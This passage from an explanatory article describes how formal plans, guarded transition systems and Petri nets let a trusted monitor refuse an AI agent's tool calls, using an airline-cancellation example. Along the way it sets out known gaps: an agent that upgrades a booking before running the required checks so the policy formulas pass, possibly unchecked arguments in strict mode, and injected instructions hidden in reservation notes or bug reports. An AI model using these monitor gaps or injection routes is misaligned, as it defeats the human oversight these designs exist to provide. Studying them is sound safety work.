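# Plans with formal execution semantics as limits on what an AI agent may do

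## What it means for a plan to have execution semantics

A plan has formal execution semantics when exact rules specify which steps may come next in every situation that can arise while it runs, and what situation each step leads to. Robot researchers worked with plans of roughly this kind from the early 1970s, and NASA later built a language for writing such plans for spacecraft. More recently, the idea has been applied to AI agents, in which a language model decides what to do and can take actions such as cancelling bookings, moving money or deleting files. If an agent's plan has exact rules, a small trusted program can check each action against the plan before the agent takes it and block any that does not fit.

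### The agent and its trace

A language model only produces text. To act, it needs tools, which are external functions such as a database query or a payment. The model writes a structured request that names a tool and gives its arguments, and other software decides what to do with the request. Anthropic's *How tool use works* states that "The model never runs anything on its own". Usually, the developer's application sends the model the user's message and a list of tools, and the model replies with one or more tool calls. The application runs them, adds the results to the conversation and sends everything back. This loop repeats until the model replies without a tool call. The agent is the model and the software that runs this loop.

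A run-time monitor is a program that intercepts each proposed call before the call runs and either allows or refuses it.

Each run leaves a trace, the ordered record of the tool calls with their arguments and results. *SOTERIA* (He, Desai and colleagues, 2026), a system that plans for agents and monitors them, represents a trace as ⟨(a₁, x₁, r₁), …, (aₖ, xₖ, rₖ)⟩, where aᵢ is the tool, xᵢ its arguments and rᵢ the result.

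The running example is an airline customer who asks an agent to cancel reservation RES123. The agent has four tools: Get-Resv looks up a reservation, No-Flown checks that the passenger has not yet flown any of its flights, Hours-Diff computes the hours since booking, and Cancel-Resv cancels the reservation. Two rules apply. The agent must first confirm through No-Flown that no flight is in the past, and the booking must be at most 24 hours old. A fuller version of the example adds exceptions for business-class and insured bookings. Cancel-Resv enforces neither rule, so an agent that calls it without making any checks will still succeed, and the customer may be happy with the outcome.

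### Why a plan in prose cannot be enforced

The easy remedy is to write the steps into the model's instructions, and most agents work this way. *From Plan to Action* (Liu, Dehghan and colleagues, 2026) examined 21,120 runs of SWE-agent, a bug-fixing agent whose standard instructions lay out four phases: find the relevant code, reproduce the bug, patch it, and validate the patch. Three of the four models tended to skip the reproduction phase. The two DeepSeek models often wrote the reproducing test before they had read the code, and the other two ran existing tests that the plan did not mention. One likely cause is the length of the conversation, because the plan appears only at the start and is followed by a growing volume of error messages and file contents. Repeating the plan every five steps raised the success rate for all four models.

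A model can also depart from a plan it wrote itself. Oota, Herrera and colleagues (2026), in *Do LLM Agents Execute the Plans They Declare?*, had three models write a plan and then act in an ordinary tool loop with the plan in view. A run counted as faithful if it matched every checkable step in the declared order, with extra actions allowed in between. The share of faithful runs ranged from 12% (Gemma-4-26B on software bugs) to 68% (DeepSeek-V4 on one of two web-browsing benchmarks). Faithfulness fell as plans got longer. On the other web benchmark, DeepSeek-V4 followed its shortest plans in 73% of runs and plans of more than ten steps in 6%.

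Some of this drift was sensible. GPT-5 mini mostly skipped reproduction on easy bugs, where the description already pointed to the fault. The plans were also engineering routines with no safety rule in them, and the models are modest by the standards of late 2026. But a stronger model did only somewhat better with the airline rules. He and colleagues report that Claude Opus 4.6, with the policy in its instructions and no monitor, broke it 11 times over 50 airline tasks. When they had a second language model judge each proposed call, the count stayed at 11.

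Better models will presumably stray from the plan less, but they will still follow it only because their training inclines them to, and nothing in the software will stop a stray call. Adding a monitor to stop such calls raises a second difficulty that better models won't remove, because the monitor must decide whether to allow each call when the agent makes it. Suppose the plan reads "check eligibility, then cancel". It is unclear whether looking up the reservation counts as the check, or whether the agent may cancel twice after checking once. A human reader settles such questions by guessing what the author meant, but a program needs the plan to specify the answers.

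### Plans as transition systems

The standard way to put them there comes from the theory of programming languages. A transition system consists of

- a set of states, one of which is the initial state;
- a set of steps, each leading from one state to another and carrying a label;
- a set of terminal states, which no step leaves.

*A Structural Approach to Operational Semantics* (Plotkin, 1981) describes finite automata, counter machines and grammars as transition systems, and uses transition systems to define what programs do. A programming language has execution semantics, in this sense, if it has rules that turn every program into a transition system. A notation for plans has execution semantics if it has rules that do the same for every plan. It hardly matters whether the plan is written as a graph, a table or code, as long as everyone who applies the rules to it gets the same transition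 system.

For an agent's plan, a label is a trace entry consisting of a call c and its result r. A step is a quadruple (s, c, r, s′), meaning that in state s, call c with result r leads to state s′. The call c is *enabled* in s if at least one step starts from s with c. The definition separates c from r because the agent chooses the call and the outside world supplies the result. The monitor must allow or block c before r exists, so it checks only whether c is enabled. Once r arrives, it looks up s′.

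A state usually has two parts, a position in the plan and the data collected so far. In a sound plan for RES123, the state just after the lookup enables only one call, No-Flown on RES123. The result "true" leads towards the age check, while "false" leads to a terminal state, from which no sequence of calls reaches Cancel-Resv.

Many authors use "plan" for something simpler. *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues, 2026), a survey of 38 studies, defines a plan as a finite sequence of actions. Such a sequence is also a transition system, with its states in a single line. Its rules are exact, but it cannot branch on what No-Flown returns, so a plan for RES123 in this form has to assume the answer in advance.

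### Plans as predictions: triangle tables

Robot planning began with plans that predicted the effects of actions. STRIPS, a planner that the Stanford Research Institute wrote for its robot Shakey, described every action by a precondition, a list of facts that the action makes true, and a list of facts that it removes. From these descriptions, STRIPS worked out a sequence of actions that would reach the goal if each action had its described effects. Real robots slip and encounter locked doors, so the researchers needed a way to detect when the prediction had failed and to tell which part of it still held.

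*Learning and Executing Generalized Robot Plans* (Fikes, Hart and Nilsson, 1972) solved this with the triangle table. The table has a row and a column for each step of the plan, plus a last row for the goal. Each cell records the facts that one step adds and that still hold when a later step is due. An extra column on the left holds the facts that the plan needs from the starting situation, and marks show which facts each step depends on. For any step i, the table shows which conditions must be true now for the steps from i to the end to reach the goal. The paper calls this set of conditions the i-th kernel. It contains everything the remaining steps and the goal require, except what those steps will supply themselves.

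Take their example, in which the robot starts in room R1 and must fetch a box from room R2 through door D1. The plan has two steps and therefore three kernels:

| Kernel | What must be true now | What the robot does |
|---|---|---|
| 3 | The box is in R1 | Stops: the goal holds |
| 2 | Robot and box are both in R2, and D1 joins R2 to R1 | Pushes the box through D1 |
| 1 | The robot is in R1, the box is in R2, and D1 joins the rooms | Goes through D1 into R2 |

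The execution program, PLANEX, tests the kernels from the highest number down and runs the step that belongs to the first true one. Then it observes the world again and repeats the test. If the robot is already in R2, PLANEX skips the first step. If the push fails to move the box, kernel 2 is still true and PLANEX pushes again. When no kernel is true, it calls STRIPS for a new plan. PLANEX keeps no record of its progress, because the facts determine the next step. The stored plans also have variables in place of particular rooms and doors, so PLANEX can sometimes route the robot around a locked door without new planning.

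These exact rules serve only to reach the goal, which can be the wrong purpose for an agent that must follow a policy. PLANEX saves a robot time by dropping any step whose effect already holds. An agent run on the same principle would skip the No-Flown check whenever its data already suggested that the customer had not travelled, even though the airline's rule requires the check itself.

### Plans as programs: PLEXIL

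In *Triangle Tables*, Nilsson (1985) later proposed extending the tables into a general language for programming robots. NASA's Plan Execution Interchange Language, PLEXIL, has a similar purpose but a different design. A PLEXIL plan is a tree of nodes. The leaves issue commands or set variables, and the inner nodes group the nodes below them. Each node has its own conditions, which take the place of built-in sequences and loops. These conditions specify when the node starts, when it ends, when it is skipped, whether it repeats, what must hold before and after it runs, and what invariant must hold while it runs.

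In a small rover plan, one node drives the rover one metre. A second node takes a picture, and its start condition requires that the first node has finished and the picture count is below ten. A third adds one to the count. A parent node containing all three repeats as long as the wheels are not stuck. The conditions determine that the rover drives before it takes a picture, so the plan doesn't need to list the steps in order.

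*A Formal Analysis Framework for PLEXIL* (Dowek, Muñoz and Păsăreanu, 2007) turned the designers' informal diagrams into a transition system. Each node is always in one of seven states, among them Waiting, Executing and Finished, and 38 rules govern how a single node changes state. For example, a Waiting node becomes Executing if its start condition and precondition both evaluate to True. Four further layers build a whole run out of these state changes. All nodes that can change state do so at the same instant, so two nodes assigning x := y and y := x swap the values. The system repeats this step and waits until no node can change state before taking in the next outside event and starting another cycle. A complete run is a number of these cycles.

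This level of detail matters in cases that prose descriptions leave out. A PLEXIL condition can be True, False or Unknown, for instance when a sensor has not reported. Under the rules of Dowek and colleagues, a node whose precondition is Unknown fails. The project's later documentation, PLEXIL (2021), lets a node start if its precondition is "not False", which on a plain reading includes Unknown. If the precondition is a safety check that has not yet returned a result, the node fails under the first rule but can start under this reading of the second.

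Dowek and colleagues also proved, with a mechanical proof checker, that PLEXIL is deterministic, meaning that two runs of the same plan end in the same state if they receive the same sequence of readings from outside. Engineers can therefore record what a spacecraft sensed and reproduce its behaviour on the ground. Similarly, a monitor that follows a deterministic plan will repeat its verdicts when given the recorded calls and results, even though a language model is not guaranteed to repeat its own behaviour.

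### Advice and permission

In PLEXIL, a node starts whenever it can. PLANEX likewise picks the step and runs it. But in a language-model agent, the model proposes a call and other software decides whether to run it, which leaves open what authority the plan has over that call.

Agre and Chapman (1988) drew a related distinction in *What are plans for?*, where they argued that what plans are like depends on how they are used. On the plan-as-program view, using a plan means executing a procedure. On the plan-as-communication view, it is more like following instructions in ordinary language, which a person has to interpret as the situation unfolds.

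SOTERIA can use the same plan as a guide or as a limit. In guided mode, the agent sees the plan as a flowchart that shrinks as results come in. The flowchart "guides but does not constrain" the agent, which may propose any call, and a monitor refuses only calls that break a rule. In strict mode, a call runs only if the plan enables it in the current state, even if the call is harmless. Suppose the customer adds, "and also look up reservation RES456", and the agent tries that lookup just before the cancellation. Guided mode allows the lookup, but strict mode refuses it because the plan enables only Cancel-Resv at that point.

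Enforcing a permission also requires tracking the plan's current state outside the model, because a model that is confused, or that has followed instructions hidden in a web page, could misreport it. *Certified Execution Harness for Agentic AI* (2026) therefore places the plan's state, the checking programs and the log of proposals in a trusted core that excludes the model.

### Plan and policy

Guided enforcement relies on rules that are separate from the plan. He and colleagues call these rules policy specifications, and each is a formula about whole traces. The formula for the first airline rule requires every call to Cancel-Resv to follow a call to No-Flown that had the same reservation number and returned true. It includes no goal and specifies no next step, and an agent that does nothing satisfies it.

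A plan defines the runs that someone intends, and a policy specification defines the runs that are acceptable. Runs(P) is the set of traces that plan P allows, and Acc(Φ) is the set of traces that satisfy every specification in the set Φ. The trace with the RES456 lookup is in Acc(Φ) but not in Runs(P), which is why the two modes treat the lookup differently.

The reverse case is more dangerous. He and colleagues give a plan for RES123 that looks up the reservation, computes its age and cancels if the booking is under the age limit. This plan would satisfy most customers, but it never calls the No-Flown check. A monitor that held the agent strictly to the plan would enforce the violation, because it would block that check if the model proposed it.

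Strict enforcement therefore protects the airline only if Runs(P) ⊆ Acc(Φ), and someone has to establish this before the first call. SOTERIA's strict mode depends on it entirely, because it runs no separate policy monitor and accepts only plans that have passed full verification. People check the specifications Φ by hand once for each domain (24 formulas cover the airline) and reuse them across tasks, while a language model writes a new plan P for each request.

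## Plan graphs with guards: how each proposed call is accepted or refused

The plans that SOTERIA checks and enforces are graphs, which He and colleagues call guarded transition systems. Each node is a stage of a procedure, and each edge leads to a next stage and may include a tool call. An edge can also carry a guard, which is a true-or-false condition on the data collected so far. The planner, a language model, writes the graph in a small programming language designed for the purpose.

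### What a plan contains

A plan declares typed variables. Some have values from the start, such as the reservation number `rid` and the current time. Others get their values from tool results, and later states can read them. Each state has one or more transitions, and a transition consists of an optional guard, at most one action, optional updates to variables, and the name of the next state. The guard comes before the action, so it cannot test the action's result. To branch on that result, a plan needs another state.

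A correct plan for cancelling RES123 could look like this, with the state names that He and colleagues use:

| State | Guard | Action | Next state |
|---|---|---|---|
| LOOKUP | none | `resv` = Get-Resv(`rid`) | CHECK_FLOWN |
| CHECK_FLOWN | none | `ok` = No-Flown(`rid`) | CHECK_AGE |
| CHECK_AGE | `ok` is true | `hrs` = Hours-Diff(booking time, `time`) | CHECK_RULES |
| CHECK_AGE | otherwise | none | NOT_PERMITTED |
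| CHECK_RULES | `hrs` ≤ 24 | none | DO_CANCEL |
| CHECK_RULES | otherwise | none | NOT_PERMITTED |
| DO_CANCEL | none | Cancel-Resv(`rid`, `reason`) | DONE |

The remaining two states are terminal. DONE is an accepting state, which means the task succeeded, and NOT_PERMITTED is a halting state, which means the agent cannot safely go on. SOTERIA rejects any plan that contains a cycle, and DO_CANCEL leads only to DONE, so Cancel-Resv can succeed at most once after the check. The language has a separate action for repeated work, which goes through a list.

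The fuller version of the airline's rules adds two guards at CHECK_RULES. One lets business-class bookings through, and the other lets insured bookings through if the reason for cancelling is health or weather. The second guard reads the variable `reason`, which the planner has to fill in from the conversation. A customer who falsely claims to be ill will pass it, because the guard tests only the recorded value.

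A plan can also call another plan. For the request "cancel my reservation and refund me", the planner writes a short parent plan that calls one sub-plan for the cancellation and another for the refund. Within the parent plan, each sub-plan works like a tool with a contract. The cancellation sub-plan requires a valid reservation number and guarantees that the reservation is either cancelled or, if the rules forbid that, left unchanged. The parent plan specifies one state to go to if the sub-plan ends in an accepting state and another if it halts. The planner therefore doesn't have to rewrite the cancellation procedure and its checks for each customer.

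Some steps need a judgement that no guard can express, such as choosing among the flights that a search returned. For these, an action called llm_eval hands the choice to the model and attaches a condition that the answer must meet. In one example, the model selects from lists of direct and one-stop flights. It must pick at least one flight, and every flight it picks must have enough seats for the passengers. SOTERIA checks the answer against this condition, queries the model again a limited number of times if the answer fails, and halts if no answer passes. The condition covers only the number of flights and the seats, so it leaves the customer's other preferences, such as a morning departure, to the model's judgement.

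### The rules of strict mode

In strict mode, the enforcing program keeps five things while a plan runs:

- q, the current plan state;
- σ, the current values of the variables;
- δ, a slot that holds at most one pending call;
- In, a queue of inputs for the model;
- Out, a history of outputs.

For RES123, q starts at LOOKUP. In σ, the user is "u42", the reservation is "RES123", the reason is "other" and the date is "2024-05-15". The slot δ is empty, and In holds the customer's message. At each step, the program applies the first rule in the following list whose condition is true.

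| Rule | Condition | Effect |
|---|---|---|
| CALL | The pending call gets approval and runs, and its result meets the tool's contract | Stores the result in σ and moves to the next state |
| CALL-REJECTED | The pending call does not get approval | Clears δ and gives the model the reason |
| POST-FAIL | The pending call runs, but its result breaks the tool's contract | Aborts the run |
| EXEC-FAIL | The pending call fails with an error, such as a network timeout | Clears δ, reports the error and stays in the same state |
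| DROP | Nothing is pending, the plan has reached an accepting state, and the model calls a tool | Discards the call silently |
| STEP | Nothing is pending, and the model replies without a tool call | Takes an input off the queue and adds to Out |
| INVOKE | Nothing is pending, the plan is unfinished, and an enabled transition matches the model's call | Puts the transition and its arguments into δ |
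| INV-GUARD | Nothing is pending, the plan is unfinished, and no enabled transition matches the call | Refuses the call and reports an error |
| CONTINUE | Nothing is pending, the plan is unfinished, and In is empty | Writes a prompt for the model to carry on |

The program always handles a pending call before it considers anything new from the model. POST-FAIL is the harshest rule because it concerns the assumptions behind the plan's verification. If Cancel-Resv returns a reservation whose status is not "cancelled", the tool's contract is wrong, and a proof that relied on it can no longer be trusted. The tool has already run by then, so aborting prevents further steps but does not undo the call.

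In STEP, the plan limits the model's tool calls but not what it writes, so an agent whose cancellation call has just been refused can still tell the customer that the booking is cancelled.

### Why a call is staged first

An accepted call takes two steps. INVOKE finds the transition that matches the call and stages it in δ with its arguments filled in, without changing anything outside the program. An approval check then examines the complete call, and CALL runs the tool only if the check approves it. The check needs the actual reservation number and must happen before the airline's database changes, because Cancel-Resv may be impossible to reverse.

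He et al. leave open what the approval check consists of. In guided mode, the policy monitor performs the check. Strict mode does not use that monitor, but a developer could still use the check for something else, such as requiring a manager's consent to large refunds.

Staging does not help once a call is under way. After a network timeout, EXEC-FAIL leaves the plan in the same state so that the model can try again. Retrying a lookup is harmless, but if the call was a payment, the bank may have moved the money before the connection dropped, and the rules would let the model send the payment again. A tool that moves money therefore needs its own protection against duplicates.

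### Cancelling RES123, step by step

The plan is at LOOKUP, and the model proposes Get-Resv on RES123. A transition matches, so INVOKE stages the call. On the next step CALL runs it, stores the reservation in `resv` and moves the plan to CHECK_FLOWN.

The model now proposes Cancel-Resv on RES123, which would skip the remaining checks. The only transition at CHECK_FLOWN calls No-Flown, so INV-GUARD refuses the cancellation and returns an error listing the available actions. The reservation is unchanged, and the plan stays at CHECK_FLOWN. The model then proposes No-Flown, which returns true, and the plan moves to CHECK_AGE. Hours-Diff returns 12 there, and the plan moves to CHECK_RULES.

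In CHECK_RULES, the program compares 12 with 24 without any input from the model. It then moves to DO_CANCEL, where it accepts only Cancel-Resv, the call it refused earlier. Cancel-Resv runs, and the plan reaches DONE. DROP discards any further tool calls from the model.

If No-Flown had returned false, the guard at CHECK_AGE would have led to NOT_PERMITTED, where the cancellation call would never run, however often the model proposed it and whatever justification it gave. The program's decision doesn't depend on why the model proposed the call, so it is the same whether the model acted hastily or followed instructions hidden in a reservation's notes.

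Guided mode also refuses the early cancellation, but for a different reason. The policy monitor provisionally adds the proposed call to the trace, without a result, and evaluates the formulas on the extended trace. It finds a Cancel-Resv with no earlier No-Flown for the same reservation. The model then receives an error message with the broken rule and an instruction to call No-Flown first.

### How far the plan fixes the arguments

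The action at DO_CANCEL is Cancel-Resv(`rid`, `reason`), and `rid` has held RES123 since the start, so the plan fixes the arguments as well as the tool. It is less clear what strict mode would do if the model asked to cancel RES456 at DO_CANCEL instead. INVOKE stages the transition with its "resolved arguments", which suggests that the program takes the values from σ and ignores the model's. The worked trace fits this reading, since the model's call to Hours-Diff appears there without arguments and still succeeds. But He and colleagues describe strict-mode refusals only for tools that the current state does not list, not for wrong arguments.

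The proof that a plan obeys the airline's rules covers only calls with the plan's own arguments. If the program compared only tool names and passed on the model's arguments, the model could check one reservation and cancel another, with no policy monitor to catch it. The program must therefore either supply the plan's arguments itself or refuse any call whose arguments differ. Guided mode does not have this gap, because the formula compares the reservation numbers in the actual calls.

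How much a variable limits the agent depends on where its value comes from. The model has no control over a refund amount that the plan computes from `resv`. But when a later step books flights that the model picked through `llm_eval`, the model has still chosen the flights, subject to the condition on seats.

### When the customer also asks about RES456

When the customer also wants RES456 looked up, guided mode allows the lookup at DO_CANCEL. In strict mode, the agent can do only what the planner anticipated, so INV-GUARD refuses the lookup even though it is harmless. Once the plan reaches DONE, DROP discards the lookup without an error message, so waiting does not help. The plan is partly at fault, because the customer made both requests in one message and the planner could have included a state for the second lookup, where strict mode would have allowed it. In SOTERIA's airline tests,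 the system wrote a new plan at each turn of the conversation, so the customer could also have asked again.

In return, strict mode also stops harmful calls that nobody thought to forbid. Guided mode depends on the policy formulas being complete, and He and colleagues had to correct some formulas and add missing ones while auditing their results. In one of their test runs, a customer asked to cancel two reservations, and an agent without a monitor upgraded one of them to business class and then cancelled it, exploiting the exception for business-class bookings. A monitor would have caught this run because the agent also skipped the flown check. But a more careful agent could upgrade the booking, look it up again, run the flown check and then cancel. That trace satisfies both of the airline's cancellation formulas, so the monitor would allow it unless another formula forbade the upgrade. A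 strict plan for an ordinary cancellation would refuse the upgrade at every state.

This protection also fails if the planner itself writes the upgrade into the plan, because a verifier working from the same formulas would accept it. Since strict mode runs only fully verified plans, it refuses any request for which the planner cannot produce one, whereas guided mode can run a partly verified plan and rely on the monitor.

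Which mode is better depends on the task. For wire transfers, or any work with a small fixed set of procedures, strict mode seems worth using even though it occasionally refuses a useful lookup. In strict mode, a customer-service agent that faces new combinations of requests all day would probably frustrate people. Guided mode suits it better, provided that someone has gone through the policy clause by clause.

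### Why a program keeps the plan state

In strict mode, the program keeps q and σ, not the model. A simpler design would leave both to the model. The model has seen every call and result, so in principle it can work out where it is in the plan and which call comes next.

Agents often act without checking the current state. *Testing the Planning Claims of LLM-Based Agents against Formal Semantics* (Miro-Lopez-Feliu, Miró López-Feliu and colleagues, 2026) tested four models on 50 tasks in five domains, such as placing patients in hospital beds and assigning web traffic to servers. The models read the tasks in plain English, while a validator checked every action against a hidden formal description that, like a STRIPS model, gave each action's preconditions and effects. In each of 1,200 offline runs, the model wrote a complete plan. In another 600 runs, the models acted online through tools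 and could ask for the current state at any time, but any action whose preconditions did not hold ended the run.

On the solvable tasks, the best offline configuration succeeded 77.5% of the time and the best online one 40%. The online agents could have done as well by fetching the whole task with four queries, planning it as in the offline test and then carrying out the plan. But only 7.3% of their actions followed a fresh check of the state, although their instructions advised them to check when unsure. Between 66% and 68% of the online runs on solvable tasks ended with an inapplicable action.

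Adding a critic, a second call to the same model to review each action, made almost no difference to these failures. The critic read the same history as the agent and, like the agent, could not query the state. The models also recognised an impossible task in only 8.9% of runs. Where a guard can detect that a task is impossible, a guarded plan moves to a halting state instead of leaving the decision to the model.

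The percentages are a poor guide to current agents because the models tested, GPT-4o, GPT-4o mini and two versions of Gemini 2.0 Flash, are old by now and had no training for long reasoning. Miro-Lopez-Feliu and colleagues draw a more durable recommendation from them, that the model should not decide whether to monitor execution and that a sound validator should catch inapplicable actions before they run. They leave open whether the agents would recover after a refusal.

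Newer models do much better at working through exact rules, but they still make mistakes. *PetriBench* (Koussios, Jäger and colleagues, 2026) tested them on Petri nets, in which places hold marks and each transition removes marks from some places and adds marks to others. It has 4,800 questions of six kinds at three levels of difficulty. Some ask how many different states the net can reach within three steps, the fewest steps needed to put a given number of marks in a place, or whether the net can get stuck. The prompt gives all the rules, and the models have no external tools. Every question has one exact answer, and guessing scores about 25%.

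| Model, at its highest reasoning setting | Easy | Medium | Hard |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 96.4% | 90.9% | 77.8% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 92.7% | 83.8% | 71.7% |
| Grok 4.6 | 95.3% | 80.9% | 56.5% |

These questions are much harder than following a cancellation plan. The hard questions that ask for the fewest steps use nets averaging about 200 places and 200 transitions, and their answers are at least 140 steps long. A plan monitor has to follow only one path, one step at a time, and the stronger models could presumably do that for a seven-state plan almost every time. Reasoning effort also affects scores a great deal. GPT-5.6 Sol scored 31.3% on the hard questions at its medium setting.

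Koussios and colleagues sampled 2,960 wrong answers and had GPT-5.6 Sol label the earliest error in each. With more reasoning effort, the models made fewer errors in searching, drawing conclusions and counting, but errors in applying the step rule, such as misjudging whether a transition was enabled, stayed about as common in the sample. This evidence is only suggestive, because humans did not check every label. The monitor's job is to apply the step rule, and a short program can do that without error.

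Longer plans are also more likely to go wrong. If a model gets each step right with probability p, independently of the others, it gets n steps right with probability pⁿ. At 99% per step, a plan with four calls succeeds about 96% of the time and one with 196 calls about 14%. In *Long-Horizon State Tracking in LLMs*, Pai and Xian (2026) had gpt-oss-120b, a fairly small open model, compute a cryptographic hash through 196 tool calls while copying four numbers exactly from one call to the next. With one provider, 21 of the 34 runs that produced an answer were right (62%), well above the 14% expected at 99% per step. Another 71 runs, some of them aborted development runs, produced no answer. The model could therefore carry exact state over a long run, but not dependably.

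In *The Illusion of Procedural Reasoning*, Samiei, Mansouri and Soleymani Baghshah (2025) tested models on finite-state machines and found that they had more trouble when each state offered many actions than when there were many states with few actions each.

Software can instead keep the state and show it to the model. *How Strongly Should Task State Influence an LLM Agent?* (Zhang, Kweon and Han, 2026) compared several ways of doing this. The agent ran procurement projects of 15 steps in which the user asked for steps out of order, cancelled some and mentioned finished ones again. It had to carry out each permitted step exactly once. With per-turn reasoning switched off, Qwen3-235B completed 38% of projects correctly when it saw only the conversation, and 55% when it also saw an accurate checklist. The figure rose to 84% when software showed it at every turn what the state implied, and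 to 98% when the software also refused wrong steps. In one run, the model wrote that a step was "already marked DONE in the checklist" and then did it again.

These gaps narrowed when the model reasoned at every turn, and the difference between telling and refusing was no longer significant. This suggests that in SOTERIA's guided mode, the flowchart will help a good model finish its task, but safety has to come from the monitor.

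Zhang and colleagues also found that enforcement did harm in one case. On a benchmark where the agent had to recognise from free text when to act, the enforcing software relied on a model's judgement of that text. When the judgement was wrong, the software enforced the mistake, and a 35-billion-parameter agent did worse than with the plain conversation. The guard `hrs` ≤ 24 avoids this problem because a program can compute it from the booking record. A guard such as "the customer is upset" would need a model's judgement, and the program would enforce that judgement just as strictly.

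## Petri nets: approvals and budgets that are used up

A guard reads a variable without changing it. That works for a condition on a booking's age, such as `hrs` ≤ 24, but less well for a manager's consent to one refund. If the plan stores the consent as `approved` = true, the value is still true after the agent has paid the refund, so a second refund passes the same guard. SOTERIA's plans have no cycles, so a single plan can rarely pay twice. But a retry after a timeout, a new plan at the next turn or a second agent sharing the approval could read the old value.

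In Petri nets, which Carl Adam Petri analysed in his 1962 dissertation, taking a step can use something up.

### Places, transitions and marks

A Petri net has places, transitions, and arrows that run from places to transitions or from transitions to places. Places hold marks. (The Petri-net literature calls them tokens, but in work on language models a token is a unit of text.) The net's state, called its *marking*, is the number of marks in each place.

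A transition is enabled if every place with an arrow into it holds at least one mark. Firing the transition removes one mark from each of those places and adds one to each place its outgoing arrows lead to, all in a single step. Arrows can also have weights. An arrow of weight 3 into a transition requires and removes three marks, and an arrow of weight 3 out of a transition adds three.

Suppose two customers want refunds. The net has three places, Waiting, Approved and Paid, and two transitions. *Approve* moves a mark from Waiting to Approved, and *pay* moves one from Approved to Paid.

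| What has just fired | Waiting | Approved | Paid | Enabled now |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| nothing | 2 | 0 | 0 | *approve* |
| *approve* | 1 | 1 | 0 | *approve*, *pay* |
| *pay* | 1 | 0 | 1 | *approve* |
| *approve* | 0 | 1 | 1 | *pay* |
| *pay* | 0 | 0 | 2 | nothing |

After the first approval, either the manager can approve the second refund or the agent can pay the first. A plan graph would need a separate state for each combination of how many refunds are waiting, approved and paid, or six states for two customers and 5,151 for a hundred. With more customers, the net keeps the same three places and only starts with more marks.

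### Why payments cannot outnumber approvals

Each transition's effect is a column of numbers, one for each place. *Approve* is (−1, +1, 0) and *pay* is (0, −1, +1). Together, the columns form the incidence matrix C. If M₀ is the starting marking and the vector y counts how often each transition has fired, then the current marking is

M = M₀ + C·y

This is the state equation. After two approvals and one payment, it gives (2, 0, 0) + 2·(−1, 1, 0) + (0, −1, 1) = (0, 1, 1), which matches the fourth row of the table.

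For the place Approved, the equation is M(Approved) = M₀(Approved) + y(*approve*) − y(*pay*). M(Approved) can never fall below zero, because a transition cannot fire when its input places lack the marks it needs. So y(*pay*) ≤ y(*approve*) + M₀(Approved), and if Approved starts empty, payments never exceed approvals during the run. The argument uses only the arrows into and out of Approved, so nobody has to list the net's states. The result holds for any number of approvals, whereas a finite automaton can count only up to a fixed limit.

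It does require that *pay* has no arrow back to Approved. With arrows in both directions, firing removes the mark and returns it at once, so one mark allows any number of payments. The condition is then *tested* rather than *spent*. Chao Gu and Quanyan Zhu, in *Certified Execution Harness for Agentic AI*, let the person who models the workflow choose between the two for each precondition. Their main example is an agent that releases software. Starting a rollout spends the reviewer's approval and a slot in the release schedule, but it only tests the mark for "no release freeze", because a release does not cause a freeze.

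A yes-or-no flag is a tested condition. Suppose a manager approves one refund of $500 and the agent, confused or under attack, requests the payment three times:

| Request | Flag before | Total paid with a flag | Marks before | Total paid with a mark |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | true | $500 | 1 | $500 |
| 2 | true | $1,000 | 0 | $500 (refused) |
| 3 | true | $1,500 | 0 | $500 (refused) |

The flag would behave like a place with at most one mark if the code cleared it after each payment. But a programmer can forget to add that line, and one flag cannot record two outstanding approvals.

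### The agentic execution Petri net

Gu and Zhu build an enforcement program around an agentic execution Petri net, in which a mark of this kind can stand for a capability, an approval, a piece of evidence or a unit of budget. Each transition has three labels: the action it stands for, the party responsible (an agent, a person or the environment), and whether the monitor can refuse it. The monitor can refuse an agent's tool calls, but not tool results, human decisions or outside incidents. When it observes an event it cannot refuse, it fires the matching transition to keep the marking up to date.

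When the model proposes an action u while the marking is M, the call runs only if it passes four checks:

1. The interface can map u to a known transition t that belongs to this agent.
2. A validator accepts the call's content, for instance because the recipient is on an allowlist.
3. The net enables t at M.
4. The supervisor permits t at M. The supervisor is a table, computed in advance, of the steps after which no uncontrollable event can lead to harm.

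Suppose a bug report contains a hidden instruction to deploy at once, and the model obeys. Its proposal maps to a known transition and may well pass the validator. But the approval place is empty, so the third check fails and the model receives an error. The model cannot add the missing mark itself, because the approving transition belongs to the reviewer and the interface maps an agent's proposals only to that agent's own transitions.

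The fourth check can block steps that the net itself allows. For example, an incident can freeze releases while a finished rollout is waiting for publication. The net still enables the publishing transition, but the supervisor blocks it because it leads to a marking that means "published during a freeze".

Gu and Zhu simulated 10,000 runs at each of several injection rates. A script stood in for the model, and 15% of the time it proposed a legitimate action two steps too early. With no checks, about 15% of runs ended in an unapproved deployment even without injections. A simulated classifier for malicious requests could not prevent these deployments, because the requests were not malicious. With the net, there were no unapproved deployments at any injection rate. This follows directly from the rule that the net never enables a rollout without an approval. Because the simulation used a script,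 it gives little evidence of how a real model would react to being refused.

### One confirmation, one mark

The inequality limits payments to the number of times *approve* fires. It limits them to the number of human decisions only if each decision fires *approve* at most once, and retries make this harder to ensure. *Beyond Single-Use Tokens* (Xu, Fan and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent that has one confirmation to transfer $500. The system issues a single-use permission and the transfer succeeds, but the acknowledgement never arrives, so the agent asks again. The system would reject the old permission, but it issues a new one for the same confirmation. The agent then transfers another $500, and *approve* has fired twice for one decision.

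Agents often repeat themselves like this. Xu and colleagues tested three model families in 10,152 runs where the outcome of a high-risk action was uncertain, and the agent proposed an equivalent call in 39.8% of them. The rate was 58% after a lost acknowledgement and 24% after a restart or a handover to another agent.

The proposed remedy, CapLease, keeps a durable record for each pair of action and confirmation. It matches a repeated request to the existing record and grants no new permission. Before the tool runs, CapLease records that the call is under way and assigns the call a key, which every retry reuses. A tool that recognises the key returns the earlier result without paying again. This would also close the gap that SOTERIA's rules leave after a network timeout. In 12,000 tests that killed and restarted processes, the combination of records and keys produced no duplicate payments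 or other effects. Duplicates still occurred with a tool that did not recognise keys.

An ordinary server-side ledger with the same records worked equally well, so the protection comes from the record, not the form of the permission. Related designs also limit how often a permission can be used. *AGENTCAP* (2026) puts a call budget and an expiry time into a signed permission, and a gateway checks what remains before each call. Santos-Grueiro's *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (2026) consumes a capability in a ledger before the call runs. The idea is older than language-model agents; *Temporary Authority, Permanent Effects* (2026) cites a 2007 paper by Bowers and colleagues on "consumable credentials". A ledger can do all of this without a Petri net, but the net adds a general way to turn a limit into a place, with a proof that the limit holds.

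### Monitor places

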